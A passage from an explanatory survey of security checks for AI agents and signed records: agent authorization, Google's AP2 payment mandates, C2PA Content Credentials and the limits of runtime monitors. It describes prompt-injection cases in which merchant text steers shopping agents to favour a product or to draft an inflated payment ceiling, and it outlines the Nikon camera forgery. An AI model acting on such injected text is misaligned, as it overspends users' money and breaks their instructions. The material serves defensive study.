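1. The people who run the system list every route by which an agent can cause a protected effect, and verify that each one passes through a check.
2. For each request, software translates the click, command or API call into a common description of its effect, such as "give Priya read access to repository 12".
3. The rule engine decides on that description and issues a ticket that works once, for one route.
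4. Just before the change takes effect, a second check confirms that the ticket, the route and the state of the repository still match.

If the agent switches from the dialog box to the command, it needs a new ticket. The researchers prove that an agent cannot evade a rule by switching among the listed routes, provided the list is complete and the translations are correct. Their procedure does not find routes missing from the list. Their example system has 12 kinds of effect and 60 routes, and a real computer has far more. They work for the company Accentrust, and they tested their own implementation on scenarios they wrote.

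### Authority gained by acquiring something

The rule engine decides whether an agent may make a call, but some calls give the agent new powers. In *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents* (Zhu and Wang, 2026), a user allows an agent to spend $20 on a rented computer that can only read certain data. The price is within the limit, the payment is valid and the purchase follows every other rule about buying. But the computer the provider delivers comes with an administrator's password and access to outside networks, which nobody meant to give the agent.

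Money is a poor measure of this risk. An agent limited to one helper program could register four free ones under different names. If the agent returns a purchase, its refund restores the budget, but a password that came with the purchase may still work.

Zhu and Wang prove that no check based only on the record of a transaction can solve the problem in general. Two purchases can have identical records but deliver different powers, so such a check must treat them the same even if only one is safe. Amazon's cloud service already handles one case by requiring one permission to start a server and another to give that server a particular set of access rights.

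The proposed remedy is to quarantine everything the agent acquires. Software queries the provider to find out what the new account or computer can do, then makes a second authorization decision based on that and everything else the agent holds. This allows rules about combinations. For example, a company could let an agent hold either an account that reads confidential files or an account that publishes to the web, but not both. The agent receives a reference that works only through a checking service, much like a capability, and never receives the password.

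The quarantine depends on the provider giving a complete and truthful account of what it has delivered. If information is missing, the item stays in quarantine, so the agent cannot use services from providers that do not supply that information. In the researchers' own tests, the system accepted all 20 safe sequences of events and rejected all 40 unsafe ones. They also examined 32 units, such as protocols and interfaces, from five outside sources, and no unit alone supplied all the information the second decision needs.

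## Signed permission to spend: the Agent Payments Protocol

Permission rules like those in Progent work when one organisation controls both the agent and its tools. When a user's agent orders something from a shop, the shop and the bank cannot see what the agent has read or what the user asked for. They receive only an order, which may reflect the user's wishes, a model's mistake or a stranger's hidden instruction. Reid, O'Callaghan and colleagues (2026), in *Risks and controls for multi-agent systems*, warn that agents dealing with each other across organisations can fail in ways that no single organisation's controls can address. The shop and the bank therefore need proof of what the user agreed to, in a form they can check themselves.

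### Signatures and access tokens

A digital signature is a code that software computes from a document and a secret key. Anyone with the matching public key can check that the holder of the secret key signed exactly that document, because changing even one character makes the check fail.

Many online services use access tokens instead. A token is a string that a program presents to show that it may make certain kinds of call, such as charging a saved card. It doesn't show what the user approved, so the same token might work for a $20 order and a $2,000 one. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Zero-Trust Runtime Verification for Agentic Payment Protocols*, point out that the signed approvals described below have much the same structure as common access tokens, but each one authorises a specific purchase.

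Google announced the Agent Payments Protocol, or AP2, in September 2025. According to PYMNTS's *Google Unveils a Payment Protocol for AI-Driven Commerce*, more than 60 firms, including American Express, Mastercard and PayPal, supported the launch. The first version mainly covered purchases that the user approves at the time. Version 0.2, released in April 2026, added purchases that an agent makes while the user is away.

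### Mandates

AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)*, the current specification, divides a purchase among five parties:

- the shopping agent, which finds products and assembles the order
- the merchant
- the credential provider, such as a digital wallet, which releases the means of payment
- the merchant's payment processor
- the trusted surface, a screen that shows the user the terms and collects their consent

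The trusted surface must not use a language model. The other parties may use one, but they must run their checks in deterministic code. The *Agent Payments Protocol Documentation* assumes that nobody can prevent prompt injection, so it treats every agent as a potential attacker.

AP2 calls a signed approval a mandate. A closed mandate approves one finished order, while an open mandate sets limits for an order that the agent has yet to find. Each comes in two parts, one for the goods and one for the money:

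| Mandate | Main contents | Who signs | Who checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Open checkout | Acceptable items, quantities and merchants | User | Merchant |
| Open payment | Limits on amount, payee, payment method and dates | User | Credential provider, card network, payment processor |
| Closed checkout | The merchant's signed order | User if present, otherwise the agent | Merchant |
| Closed payment | Exact amount, payee and payment method | User if present, otherwise the agent | Credential provider, card network, payment processor |

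This split lets the wallet and the card network check a payment without learning what the user bought. To link the two parts, both closed mandates contain the same hash, a short code computed from the merchant's signed order. Any change to the order changes the hash.

"User" in the table covers two arrangements. In the first, the user signs with the key of a digital credential from an issuer that the shop trusts. In the second, the agent's provider shows the user the terms on its own screen and then signs with its own key. The second arrangement is simpler to set up, but it puts the provider in the trusted base, and the provider must make sure that the agent cannot use the key.

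### A purchase with the user present

One of AP2's examples is the purchase of a Holland Lop rabbit for $150:

1. The agent assembles the order, and the merchant signs it.
2. The agent drafts the two closed mandates and sends them to the trusted surface.
3. The trusted surface shows the user the rabbit, the merchant and the price. The user approves, for instance with a fingerprint, and the trusted surface signs both mandates.
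4. The agent sends the payment mandate to the credential provider, which checks it and returns a payment token for this purchase.
5. The agent sends that token and the checkout mandate to the merchant. The merchant compares the mandate with the order it signed, and the payment processor checks that the token belongs to that order.
6. The merchant and the payment processor return signed receipts.

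If the agent changes the payment to $180 after step 3, the signature no longer matches and the credential provider won't release the token. If the merchant raises the price, the new order has a different hash, which neither mandate contains. The hash also stops a thief from using the payment mandate for a different $150 order.

### A purchase within limits

In another of AP2's examples, the user wants a limited-edition pair of shoes and will be away when the agent buys them. The user signs open mandates for one pair, in one size, from one merchant, for at most $200 and within the next hour. The mandates include the agent's public key, so a program that steals them cannot use them without the agent's secret key.

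The agent later finds the shoes for $199, and the merchant signs the order. The agent signs the closed mandates with its own key and presents them together with the user's open ones. Here is how the checks would treat that order and several variations:

| Order | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| One pair for $199 | accepted | Meets every limit |
| One pair for $210 | rejected | Price above $200 |
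| Two pairs for $99 each | rejected | Wrong quantity |
| A different shoe for $150 | rejected | Item not on the list |
| The same shoe from another shop for $180 | rejected | Merchant not on the list |
| One pair for $199, two hours later | rejected | Mandate expired |
| One pair for $200 from a merchant that usually charges $120 | accepted | Meets every limit |

If the mandates contain limits c₁ to cₙ, a purchase p passes only if all of them hold:

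c₁(p) ∧ c₂(p) ∧ … ∧ cₙ(p).

Some limits take more work to check. Suppose a mandate permits one pair of shoes, either red or blue, and one pair of socks. The software has to match each item in the order to its own slot in the mandate and leave no slot empty. An order for red shoes and socks passes, but an order for red shoes and blue shoes fails because both pairs need the shoe slot and nothing fills the sock slot.

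If a verifier does not recognise a limit, it must treat that limit as failed, in line with Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults. It can also ask for the user to return and approve the finished order. But a missing limit imposes no restriction, so if the open payment mandate contains no list of payees, the payment check accepts any payee.

The limits in the shoe example apply to each order separately. A hijacked agent could sign two orders for the same shoes at once, and each would meet every limit, though together they cost $398. AP2 forbids an agent to reuse an open mandate unless it has a receipt showing that the previous attempt failed. Since AP2 treats the agent as a potential attacker, something outside the model must enforce that rule. The documentation suggests having ordinary code guard the agent's key and check each mandate before signing. Credential providers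 and payment processors may also reject overlapping mandates, but the specification does not require them to.

Software can reliably enforce single use when one program keeps the record of which permissions have been used. Wu and colleagues tested a one-time permission for a money transfer by making 32 simultaneous attempts to use it. In each of 100 trials, exactly one attempt succeeded. In AP2, the credential provider is well placed to keep this record because it releases the means of payment.

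A mandate for repeated purchases also needs a running count. For example, it can permit one payment a month, up to twelve payments and $1,000 in total. Progent's rules cannot express such a limit.

### What the signatures guarantee

A completed payment comes with an unaltered approval that anyone can trace to a particular key, provided that the keys stay secret, the trusted surface shows the real terms, and every party makes its checks. The approval covers either the exact order or limits that the order stays within.

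The signatures do not guarantee that the user understood the terms, or that the agent chose well within the limits. The merchant in the last row of the table charges $80 more than usual, yet every check passes. AP2 relies on the limits to cap the loss, which works only if the user set sensible limits and nobody can use the mandate twice.

The price and payee are better protected than the items, because the credential provider checks them independently, while only the merchant checks the items. A dishonest merchant could skip that check and accept an agent's order for the wrong shoe at $199. The payment would still pass the credential provider's checks, since the amount and payee are permitted, and the mistake would come to light only when the user complained.

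### Attacks that leave the signatures valid

In *Whispers of Wealth*, Debi, Zhu and Sen Gupta (2026) built a shopping agent on the first version of AP2, using Gemini 2.5 Flash, and asked it for outdoor basketball shoes. The agent ranked a product first in all ten trials when the merchant's description of it contained hidden instructions, and never without them. Acting as a malicious user, the researchers also tried to obtain other customers' data and succeeded in two of ten trials.

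Ten successes out of ten are consistent with a true success rate as low as about 74 per cent (0.74¹⁰ ≈ 0.05), which is still very high. But the researchers measured which product came first, not whether anyone bought it. A user who was present would still see the product and the price before signing. The customer data leaked because access control failed, which no mandate addresses.

When an agent makes a purchase while the user is away, an attacker can target the mandate's limits. *Beyond the Mandate* (Aviv, Gandh and colleagues, 2026) gives an example based on version 0.2. A user asks for one camera costing no more than $50. The merchant claims in its product information that the purchase may need some headroom, and the agent drafts a mandate for up to $80 with no restriction on the payee. A second agent, meant to catch such differences, accepts the explanation because a careless update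 has loosened its instructions. The trusted surface presents the higher ceiling as headroom, the user approves it, and the merchant charges $80 with every signature valid.

Aviv and colleagues recommend moving the comparison into fixed code outside the model. The trusted surface should reject a ceiling above the user's stated limit, show the exact maximum, and warn the user when the mandate does not restrict the payee. This would help only if software had recorded the $50 limit before the merchant's text could influence the agent.

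The camera attack is one of five that the researchers demonstrated. They catalogued 48 threats and rated eight as high risk. Several involve weaknesses outside the mandates. In one, a credential provider that serves many merchants fails to keep their records separate and releases one merchant's payment tokens to another, which makes it a confused deputy. In another, an attacker gets the agent to fall back to the first version of the protocol, which lacks the newer defences against reuse.

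Eight outside experts agreed with the original risk level in 111 of 120 ratings, so the ratings are fairly consistent. But the risk level can depend on where the cut-off is set, since reuse of a mandate scored up to 6.7 out of 10, just short of the 7.0 needed for "high". Aviv and colleagues had to build their own test system, so the demonstrations show that the attacks can work but not how often they would work against a real shop.

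The automatic scanner found 14 of 18 threats in that system. One of the four it missed was misleading text planted before the user signs, when several agents share the work. Software can fully verify a signature, but it has no comparable way to check whether a merchant's text has misled an agent.

Lan and colleagues at eBay studied the reuse of mandates in the protocol's first version. They simulated a verifier that checked only signatures and expiry dates, and it stopped none of the copied or redirected mandates. They then added a number that works only once and a hash of the task, agent, merchant and permitted action. The new verifier stopped every attack and took about 3.8 milliseconds per check, even at 10,000 transactions a second. The short checking time is the more useful result, since the researchers designed the new checks for exactly these attacks and it is unsurprising that they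 stopped them all.

### Governance and adoption

In April 2026, Google gave AP2 to the FIDO Alliance, an industry association known for its work on passkeys. Members from Mastercard and Visa chair the alliance's payments group, according to Help Net Security's *FIDO Alliance wants to keep AI agents from going rogue* (2026). The group will review and develop the protocol, so version 0.2 is not yet a finished standard.

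Mastercard contributed its own scheme, Verifiable Intent, to the same group. It developed the scheme with Google to work alongside AP2. The Paypers' *Google donates the Agent Payments Protocol to FIDO Alliance* describes it as a tamper-proof log of what the user authorised an agent to do and when. A log is mainly useful afterwards, for establishing what happened. AP2 produces such a record too, but its mandates also let the merchant and the credential provider refuse a purchase before any money moves.

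Use of AP2 seems limited. In August 2026, Aviv and colleagues found no complete public deployment, and Google's public code covered only part of the protocol. AP2 is also an optional extension to the Universal Commerce Protocol (UCP), a broader standard for purchases through agents. Under the August version of UCP, AP2 is active only when both the business and the agent's platform declare support.

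Merchants may end up supporting several schemes. In September, *Ant International, Visa, Mastercard work to make agentic protocols interoperable* (McConvey, 2026) reported that the three companies were trying to make agent protocols work together. In October, *The Alphabet Soup of Agentic Standards* (PYMNTS, 2026) advised merchants not to wait for a single winner, because there probably won't be one.

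### Who has to prove what

When a purchase made through AP2 goes wrong, the law and the card network's rules still determine who pays. AP2 supplies evidence, which can change what each side has to explain.

Suppose a customer denies ordering the $199 shoes. Without a mandate, the merchant can show only that an agent placed the order, and has to argue that the agent was acting for the customer. With a mandate, the card network can recompute the hash of the merchant's order, check the signatures and match the receipts to the mandates. If these checks pass, the customer has to explain why the approval should not count, for example because somebody stole the key or the screen showed different terms.

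The record can also show that a business was at fault. If the merchant charged $210, the signed limit of $200 shows that the credential provider should have refused the payment. If the merchant sent the wrong shoes, the order it signed lists the right ones.

The customer with the $80 camera is in a weaker position than before. The mandate contains the $80 ceiling but not the conversation in which the customer asked for a $50 limit, so the signed evidence supports the merchant. To prove that request, the customer would need the agent's chat history, which the agent's provider may hold. If that provider also signed the mandate on the customer's behalf, it has an interest in defending its consent screen.

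Some disputes will lack a complete record. A mandate may name only an online marketplace and not the seller behind it. Aviv and colleagues also warn that rules requiring companies to delete personal data could destroy evidence. AP2 doesn't specify how mandates are stored or retrieved, so a customer may have to rely on the merchant to keep the mandate that supports the customer's claim against it.

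## Signed origin records for media: Content Credentials

Digital signatures, which AP2 uses to let a shop check what a user approved, can also let a reader check where a photograph, video or recording came from. The Coalition for Content Provenance and Authenticity (C2PA), an industry group that includes Adobe, Google, Microsoft, Meta and Amazon, publishes an open standard for this. Under the standard, a camera, editing program or image generator attaches a signed record to each file of how it made or changed that file. These records are publicly called Content Credentials.

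Leica sold the first consumer camera with Content Credentials in October 2023, according to *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026). OpenAI first used them in 2024, on images from DALL·E 3, according to its *Advancing content provenance*.

### How software signs and checks a file

The technical specification from C2PA (2026) calls the record a manifest. A manifest contains assertions, which are statements about the file, such as which camera took the picture. It also contains a claim that lists the assertions, and a signature on the claim.

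One assertion holds a hash of the file. Let x be the part of the file that the hash covers, and H the function that computes it. The signing program computes H(x) and signs a claim that covers the result. A reader's software later computes H(x′) from the file it received, and the file passes only if

H(x′) = H(x).

Replacing the stored hash to match an altered picture would break the signature.

The software also checks the signer's certificate, a signed statement that a key belongs to a particular device or program. It can then place the manifest in one of three nested categories:

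- A well-formed manifest follows the rules of the format.
- A valid manifest has also stayed unchanged since somebody signed it, with a certificate that was in date and that the software has not found to be revoked.
- A trusted manifest also has a certificate from an authority on the software's list of trusted authorities.

C2PA maintains the main list of trusted certificate authorities, and users can add others. Anyone can make their own certificate and sign a manifest with it, so a manifest can be valid without being trusted.

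### From an image generator to a newspaper

Suppose a designer uses an AI generator to make a picture of a flooded street, crops it, and sends it to a newspaper for an article about future floods. Every program involved supports Content Credentials.

1. The generator creates the picture and writes the first manifest. In simplified form, and based on an example in the Content Authenticity Initiative's *Writing assertions and actions*, the assertion about its origin looks like this:

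```
action:             c2pa.created
digitalSourceType:  trainedAlgorithmicMedia
softwareAgent:      Tool XYZ
```

2. The editing program opens the picture, checks the first manifest against it and records the result. After the crop, it signs a second manifest with a new hash. The first manifest stays in the file as the history of an "ingredient".
3. The newspaper's system adds a third manifest, which states that it published the picture. The pixels have not changed, so this manifest needs no new hash.
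4. A reader's software checks the latest signature and the hash of the cropped picture, then displays the history back to the generator.

The value `trainedAlgorithmicMedia` in the record marks media as AI-generated. C2PA's *Use of Content Credentials to Identify Synthetic and Non Synthetic Content* (2026) explains that if AI changes only part of a photograph, the manifest can mark the changed region.

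In step 4, the software cannot check the first manifest against the generator's original picture, because the file contains only the cropped version. It relies on the editing program's record that the check passed in step 2. The trusted base therefore includes every program that signed along the way.

The designer could also crop the picture in a program that doesn't support Content Credentials, and the hash would no longer match the picture. According to an explainer from C2PA, if she then signs it again in a program that does support them, the new signer implicitly vouches for the crop. If she deletes the first manifest before step 2, the editing program receives a picture with no history, so the reader can't learn anything about the generator from that program's signature.

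### What a valid record proves

A valid, trusted record proves that a particular signer made certain statements about a file, and that the part of the file covered by the hash has not changed since. It doesn't prove that the statements are true, and C2PA's explainer says that provenance alone cannot establish whether a picture is accurate.

A photographer can stage a scene and sign an unaltered photograph of it. Somebody can post a signed photograph of an old flood and claim in the caption that the flood happened last night. If a signing camera photographs a good print of an AI-generated picture, its record of that photograph will be correct. In each case the software works as designed, and the reader is misled only by inferring more than is in the record.

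The signer is usually a device or a program, so the record need not identify the photographer. Readers have to check the record itself, because anyone can paste the Content Credentials icon onto a picture. *Media Integrity and Authentication* (2026), a Microsoft report, lists this among the system's weaknesses.

### The Nikon Z6III

In August 2025, Nikon added Content Credentials to its Z6III camera through a firmware update. Nikon said the service was mainly for media organisations and for creators who need a high level of trust. About a week later, a user, Adam Horshack, found a way to make the camera sign a picture it had not taken. Nikon Rumors published his report on 3 September in *Major vulnerability in Nikon’s C2PA feature on the Z6 III* (2025).

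The flaw was in the multiple-exposure function, which blends several shots into one picture. The user can choose an existing raw file, which holds unprocessed image data, as the first shot. Videomaker's *Nikon announces temporary suspension of its Authenticity Service* describes the first demonstration:

1. Horshack photographed a graphic reading "Hacked by Horshack!" with a second Z6III that did not have the signing feature.
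2. He moved the memory card to the signing camera and selected that photograph as the first exposure.
3. He took the second exposure with the lens cap on. Blending the photograph with a black frame left it unchanged.
4. The camera signed the result, and a public checking site accepted it.

He later converted an AI-generated picture of a pug flying an aeroplane to Nikon's raw format and had the camera sign that too. PetaPixel's *Nikon Can’t Fully Solve the Z6 III’s C2PA Problems Alone* (2025) emphasises that the signed picture was an exact digital copy of the AI image, not a photograph of a screen.

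The camera's part of the system can be written as an interface contract:

- Assumption: every image that reaches the signing step comes from this camera's sensor, or from a file whose origin the camera has checked.
- Guarantee: every picture the camera signs was made only from such images.

Multiple exposure made the assumption false. Z System User's *Content Inauthentication* explains that the camera did not check whether the chosen raw file was authentic, so nobody had to break the hash or the signature. A FIDES-style rule for combining labels would have marked a blend of a trusted and an untrusted exposure as untrusted, and the camera would have refused to sign it.

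Nikon suspended the service on 5 September, according to PetaPixel's *Nikon Suspends C2PA Functionality on the Z6 III Due to Authentication Issue* (2025). The suspension only prevented users from installing new certificates. Cameras that already had one could still sign images, so Nikon announced that it would revoke every certificate it had issued (Digital Camera World, *Nikon revokes all C2PA image authenticity certificates after major vulnerability exposed*). *Verifying Provenance of Digital Media* (Golaszewski, Krawetz and colleagues, 2026), a security analysis of the standard, dates the revocation to November 2025.

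### How revocation works

Nikon cannot change files that people have already copied. An issuer revokes a certificate by reporting that it is no longer valid, which has an effect only if the reader's software receives that report.

C2PA provides two ways to check a certificate's status. A signing program can attach a signed statement of the status from the issuer. If the file contains no usable statement, the reader's software may query the issuer online. The online check is optional because it could reveal to an observer which picture someone is viewing. Software that skips the check records that it did so, but does not reject the manifest.

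A forged picture can therefore still pass as valid after its certificate is revoked. When Golaszewski and colleagues examined one of the forged Nikon pictures after the revocation, Adobe's checking tool reported the signature as valid and another tool, Verifieddit, reported it as invalid. Neither reported that Nikon had revoked the certificate. The researchers want revocation checks to be compulsory, using downloadable lists of revoked certificates. Software that downloads a whole list does not disclose which picture it is checking, but the standard forbids such lists.

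A compulsory check would also reject genuine photographs, because Nikon's certificates had signed those as well as the forgeries, and a reader cannot tell the two apart by the signature.

### Other gaps in the guarantee

The hash doesn't have to cover the whole file, and somebody can change the excluded part without invalidating the signature. This lets a photographer remove a location later, for example. Google's Pixel 10 Pro left the location out of the hash. Golaszewski and colleagues replaced it with a false one, and a checking tool displayed the false location without a warning.

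They also found that someone can replace the trusted time-stamp, a separate signed statement of when the signing happened, because nothing in the signed data refers to it. Without a usable time-stamp, the software must compare the certificate's expiry date with the current date, so an old record can fail the checks once its certificate expires. A picture from a pilot by Arizona's Secretary of State passed the checks in January 2025 and failed a year later, although the file had not changed.

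C2PA's product certification programme relies largely on what companies report about themselves and does not examine their code. Golaszewski and colleagues conclude that nobody should yet depend on the standard for journalism, legal evidence or financial disclosures. Most of these faults look repairable. The Pixel 10 Pro and version 2.3 of the specification incorporated some of the researchers' suggestions, but version 2.4, released in April 2026, addressed none of their remaining concerns.

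### Why a missing record proves little

A screenshot contains none of the original file's manifest. Re-encoding a picture also removes the manifest, as do most ways of uploading one, according to *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI*. C2PA's security notes state that the design does not protect against complete removal of the manifest.

A missing record is weak evidence of whether a picture is AI-generated. Suppose a website has 1,000 pictures, of which 900 are photographs and 100 are AI-generated, and that 5 per cent of the photographs and 40 per cent of the AI pictures still have a record when they appear there. That leaves 855 photographs and 60 AI pictures without one. About 6.6 per cent of the pictures without a record are AI-generated, compared with 10 per cent of all the pictures, so in this example a missing record makes AI generation slightly less likely.

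If 95 per cent of the photographs kept their records, only 45 would lack one, and 57 per cent of the pictures without records would be AI-generated. *From Forensics to Ecosystems* (2026) makes the general point that a missing record becomes a reason for suspicion only if people attach records to all kinds of content and websites preserve them.

Websites have a poor record of doing so. In October 2025, the Washington Post uploaded a video from OpenAI's Sora to eight platforms. Only YouTube disclosed that it was AI-generated, and its notice was hard to find, according to *Platform Transparency Falters*. OpenAI said it added Content Credentials to every Sora video, according to the Post's article, which the AI Incident Database reproduced. In *OpenAI does not appear to be applying watermarks honestly*, a user who tested this reported finding them only on videos downloaded without the visible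 watermark.

A March 2026 audit by the publication Indicator found better results for some combinations of generator and platform. IPTC, a standards body for the news industry, reports in *AI disclosure on social media* that LinkedIn, Pinterest and YouTube correctly labelled all the images and videos from OpenAI's models. Instagram recognised some images from Meta AI, but LinkedIn, TikTok and YouTube did not. Meta AI marks its images with a metadata field that IPTC defines.

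### Watermarks as a backup

An invisible watermark is a pattern in the pixels that software can read and people can hardly see. Because it is part of the picture, it can survive a screenshot or compression that removes the manifest. It can mark the picture as AI-generated or point to a copy of the manifest in an online store. Software can also search such a store by fingerprint, a code computed from the picture's appearance that stays similar when the picture changes slightly. C2PA calls a record with a watermark or fingerprint as backup a durable Content Credential.

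Suppose a website removes the flood picture's manifest and compresses the picture. A reader's software finds the watermark and fetches the stored manifest, but the hash no longer matches because compression changed the file. The software cannot tell from the hash whether somebody altered the picture or the watermark led to the wrong manifest. The reader can compare the picture with the small preview that many manifests contain, but no longer has proof that nothing changed.

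*Media Integrity and Authentication* recommends watermarks for information that is not critical to security. Moving a watermark from one picture to another is difficult but possible, especially with AI techniques. An attacker could do this to make a genuine photograph appear AI-generated.

### Detectors that judge the picture itself

A detector examines a picture for signs of AI generation without help from whoever made the picture. It can therefore assess the many files that have no origin record, though its result is only an estimate.

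Recent tests suggest that detectors' estimates are often poor on the pictures people most want to check. For *WildAIGC-Bench*, Yu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) collected 600 AI-generated or edited images that had circulated as evidence for claims about public events, along with 638 genuine photographs of related subjects. All ten visual detectors did worse on this collection than they did on average across eight other benchmarks. For 37 per cent of the AI images, at least three-quarters of the detectors classified the image as real.

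Partial edits are particularly hard to detect. In one test in *AI-Generated Image Detectors Exploit Global Artifacts* (2026), two commercial detectors scored about 0.55 on photographs with an AI-made region, where guessing would give 0.5. Across 16 detectors, those that had done best on ordinary edits generally lost the most accuracy in the harder test, which suggests they had been detecting side effects of the editing process rather than the new content.

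Detectors also wrongly flag genuine photographs as AI-generated. *Déjà VAE* (2026) reports such errors on degraded photographs, and finds that a widely used benchmark overstates how well detectors work in practice. Even a fairly good detector can make many of these errors. Suppose one catches 90 per cent of AI pictures and wrongly flags 5 per cent of photographs. On the website with 900 photographs and 100 AI pictures, it would flag 90 AI pictures and 45 photographs, so a third of the pictures it flagged would be genuine.

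A forger with access to a detector can keep altering a picture until it passes. This trial and error doesn't work against a signature, but a forger who only wants to hide that a picture is AI-generated can delete the signed record.

### Laws that require marking

The EU and California now require companies to mark AI-generated media. The main dates are:

| Duty | Who must comply | Applies from |
|---|---|---|
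| EU: machine-readable marks on AI output | Providers of systems placed on the market on or after 2 August 2026 | 2 August 2026 |
| EU: the same marks | Providers of older systems | 2 December 2026 |
| EU: disclosure of deepfakes | Those who use AI to make them | 2 August 2026 |
| California: a hidden mark, an optional visible label and a free detection tool | Providers with over one million monthly users | 2 August 2026 |
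| California: detection of origin records in posted content | Large online platforms | 1 January 2027 |
| California: an option to add a hidden mark | Makers of new cameras and other recording devices | 1 January 2028 |

Article 50(2) of the EU AI Act requires synthetic audio, images, video and text to be marked. Older systems had until 2 December 2026 to comply, according to Lewis Silkin's *Council of the EU gives AI Omnibus final green light* (2026). Net Influencer's *The EU AI Act and the Creator Economy* reports that the duty to disclose deepfakes had no such grace period. Fines can reach €15 million or 3 per cent of worldwide annual turnover, whichever is higher, according to FEDIL, a Luxembourg business federation. The European Commission has published guidelines and a voluntary code of practice.

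The first duties under California's AI Transparency Act took effect on 2 August 2026, according to Morgan Lewis' *New California AI Disclosure Rules Become Operative* (2026). The law uses the term "manifest disclosure" for the visible label, which is unrelated to a C2PA manifest. Orrick's *California delays its AI Transparency Act and passes new content laws* (2025) says the required detection tool identifies content from the provider's own system. Somebody who doesn't know which generator made a picture may therefore have to try several tools.

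The platform rule, summarised in the California Legislature's *California Assembly Bill 853*, refers to "widely adopted specifications" from an established standards body. C2PA is an obvious candidate, and Adobe's *C2PA metadata in AI Assistant* describes it as the company's tool for complying with transparency laws. Under the 2028 rule, manufacturers only have to offer an optional mark, so photographers can still take genuine pictures without one.

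## What the systems have in common and where they differ

The main systems differ in what they guarantee, when they check it, and whose information the check relies on.

| System | Property guaranteed | Where it is checked | When | Trusted base | Who supplies labels or rules |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Google's safe coding | Only text that developers wrote shapes a database command | Types of the database functions | Compile time | Compiler, builder functions, reviewed exceptions | Security engineers |
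| FIDES | Untrusted text cannot choose an action, or data reaches only permitted readers, depending on the tool | Agent loop | Each call | Loop, tool wrappers, labels, policies | Agent's developer |
| Labels sent over MCP | Much the same as FIDES, but across organisations | Client | Each call | Client, server, labels, policies | Server's operator, with additions by the client |
| LLMbda | Hidden data does not affect visible results, except through whether the program finishes | Interpreter and tools | Each step and each call | Lean, the connection to the model, labels, checks in tools | Agent's developer |
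| TACIT | A program cannot reveal classified text | Scala compiler, with some checks in the library | Compile time, then run time for details such as file paths | Compiler, library, runtime, local model | Library's author, and the owner who marks files |
| Progent and Cedar | No call outside the rules reaches a tool | Rule engine | Each call | Engine, rules, routing of calls | User, administrator or a language model |
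| AP2 | A payment matches terms that somebody signed | Merchant, credential provider, payment processor | Receipt | Keys, trusted surface, each verifier | User |
| Content Credentials | The covered part of a file is unchanged since a known signer signed it | Reader's software | Receipt | Signing devices and programs, keys, certificate authorities | Signing device or program |

No trusted base in the table includes the model that plans an agent's actions. Each check examines something that ordinary software can fully inspect, such as a type, an amount or a hash. Someone still has to supply the facts that software cannot work out, such as which files are secret.

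A compile-time check covers every input a program might receive and adds no work while the program runs, but it cannot use values that are known only at run time. A check on each call can use those values, such as the actual recipient and amount. Checking a document on receipt works between organisations that cannot inspect each other's software, but it can verify only what the document contains.

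### What a monitor can enforce

Several of these systems rely on a monitor, which follows a program's steps and stops the program before it takes a forbidden one. Schneider (2000), in *Enforceable Security Policies*, proved a limit on what monitors of this kind can enforce. His argument rests on three facts about them:

1. A monitor judges each run by itself. The policy must therefore be a test that every single run has to pass.
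2. A monitor cannot let a violation through in the hope that a later step will put it right, because the run might end first. If a partial run fails the test, every continuation of it must fail too.
3. A monitor has to act at some definite point. If a run fails the test, it must already have failed after a finite number of steps.

A policy that fits all three is a safety property, a rule that some bad thing never happens. Schneider showed that these monitors can enforce only safety properties.

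His simplest example is a rule against sending messages after reading a file. The monitor has two states. It starts in "no file read", where it allows every step. When the program reads a file, the monitor moves to "file read", where it allows every step except sending. The label on a FIDES conversation plays the same role as the monitor's state, but it can take more values.

No monitor can enforce a rule that the email assistant must eventually answer every message, because however long the owner has waited, the answer might still come. Adding a one-hour deadline makes this a safety property, but the monitor still cannot enforce it, because the deadline will pass even if the monitor stops the assistant. Schneider also considers a seller who has taken a customer's money. A monitor can prevent the seller from doing anything else before providing the service, but cannot make the seller provide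 it. Similarly, AP2 lets a credential provider refuse a bad payment but cannot ensure that the shoes are delivered.

Blocking extra runs never violates a safety property, so engineers can run several monitors together and enforce all their rules at once. For the same reason, a monitor can be far too strict, even blocking everything, and still be secure.

### Why secrecy is different

Checking whether a system keeps a secret requires comparing its possible runs. Suppose an assistant has read its owner's medical result, which is positive or negative, and then proposes a meeting to a colleague at noon or at one o'clock. If all four combinations of result and time are equally likely, the colleague learns nothing about the result from the time.

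Suppose a monitor blocks the runs "positive, one o'clock" and "negative, noon". The two remaining runs are unchanged, but the colleague can now work out the result from the time. Blocking runs has created a leak, which could not happen if secrecy were a safety property.

No one could detect the leak from one run either, because a record of a positive result followed by a proposal for noon does not show whether the assistant would have proposed noon anyway. Integrity raises the same problem, because whether a stranger's email influenced an action depends on what the agent would have done without it.

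A monitor can still prevent leaks by enforcing a stricter rule that implies secrecy, as Schneider points out. For example, it can enforce "Never send anything labelled private to an outsider", because a single run is enough to show a violation. This rule prevents leaks only if the labels account for every influence, including that of branches the program did not take. FIDES's labels do not account for those branches, while LLMbda stops the program when a secret is about to affect public data in this way.

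A compiler can avoid the problem because it reads the whole program, including every branch, before any run begins. Schneider therefore placed compilers and theorem provers outside his class of monitors. TACIT uses this advantage when it requires functions that handle secret text to be pure.

### When untrusted text must decide the action

Labels protect an action by keeping untrusted text from choosing it, but some tasks require the agent to act on what a stranger wrote. Costa and colleagues give a formal test for their distinction between data-independent and data-dependent tasks. Let T(d) be the set of action sequences that would complete a task if the agent's storage contained d. The task is data-independent if

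⋂ T(d) ≠ ∅,

where the intersection covers all the possible contents d. In other words, one sequence works whatever the data turns out to be. Forwarding three emails unread passes this test, but adding a meeting only if an email asks for one fails it.

FIDES can handle some data-dependent tasks by restricting the quarantined model's answer to a short list. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*, takes this further by deciding separately what untrusted text may contribute to each part of an action. In one of his examples, a coding agent reads the log of a failed software test, which an attacker may have influenced:

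| Part of the action | What the log may contribute |
|---|---|
| Which tool to run | Nothing |
| Which file to edit | A path, once trusted code has checked it for this purpose |
| The new contents of the file | Material for a change, which needs authorization for its exact effect |
| Whether somebody has approved the change | Nothing |
| A comment that explains the failure | A quotation, which counts as untrusted if another agent reads it |

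The agent also needs separate permission to act. That permission works only once, because otherwise a log could cause the agent to repeat an action that was harmless the first time. Before running the action, a program checks that all these permissions refer to the same action, so an attacker cannot combine a path approved for one edit with permission granted for another.

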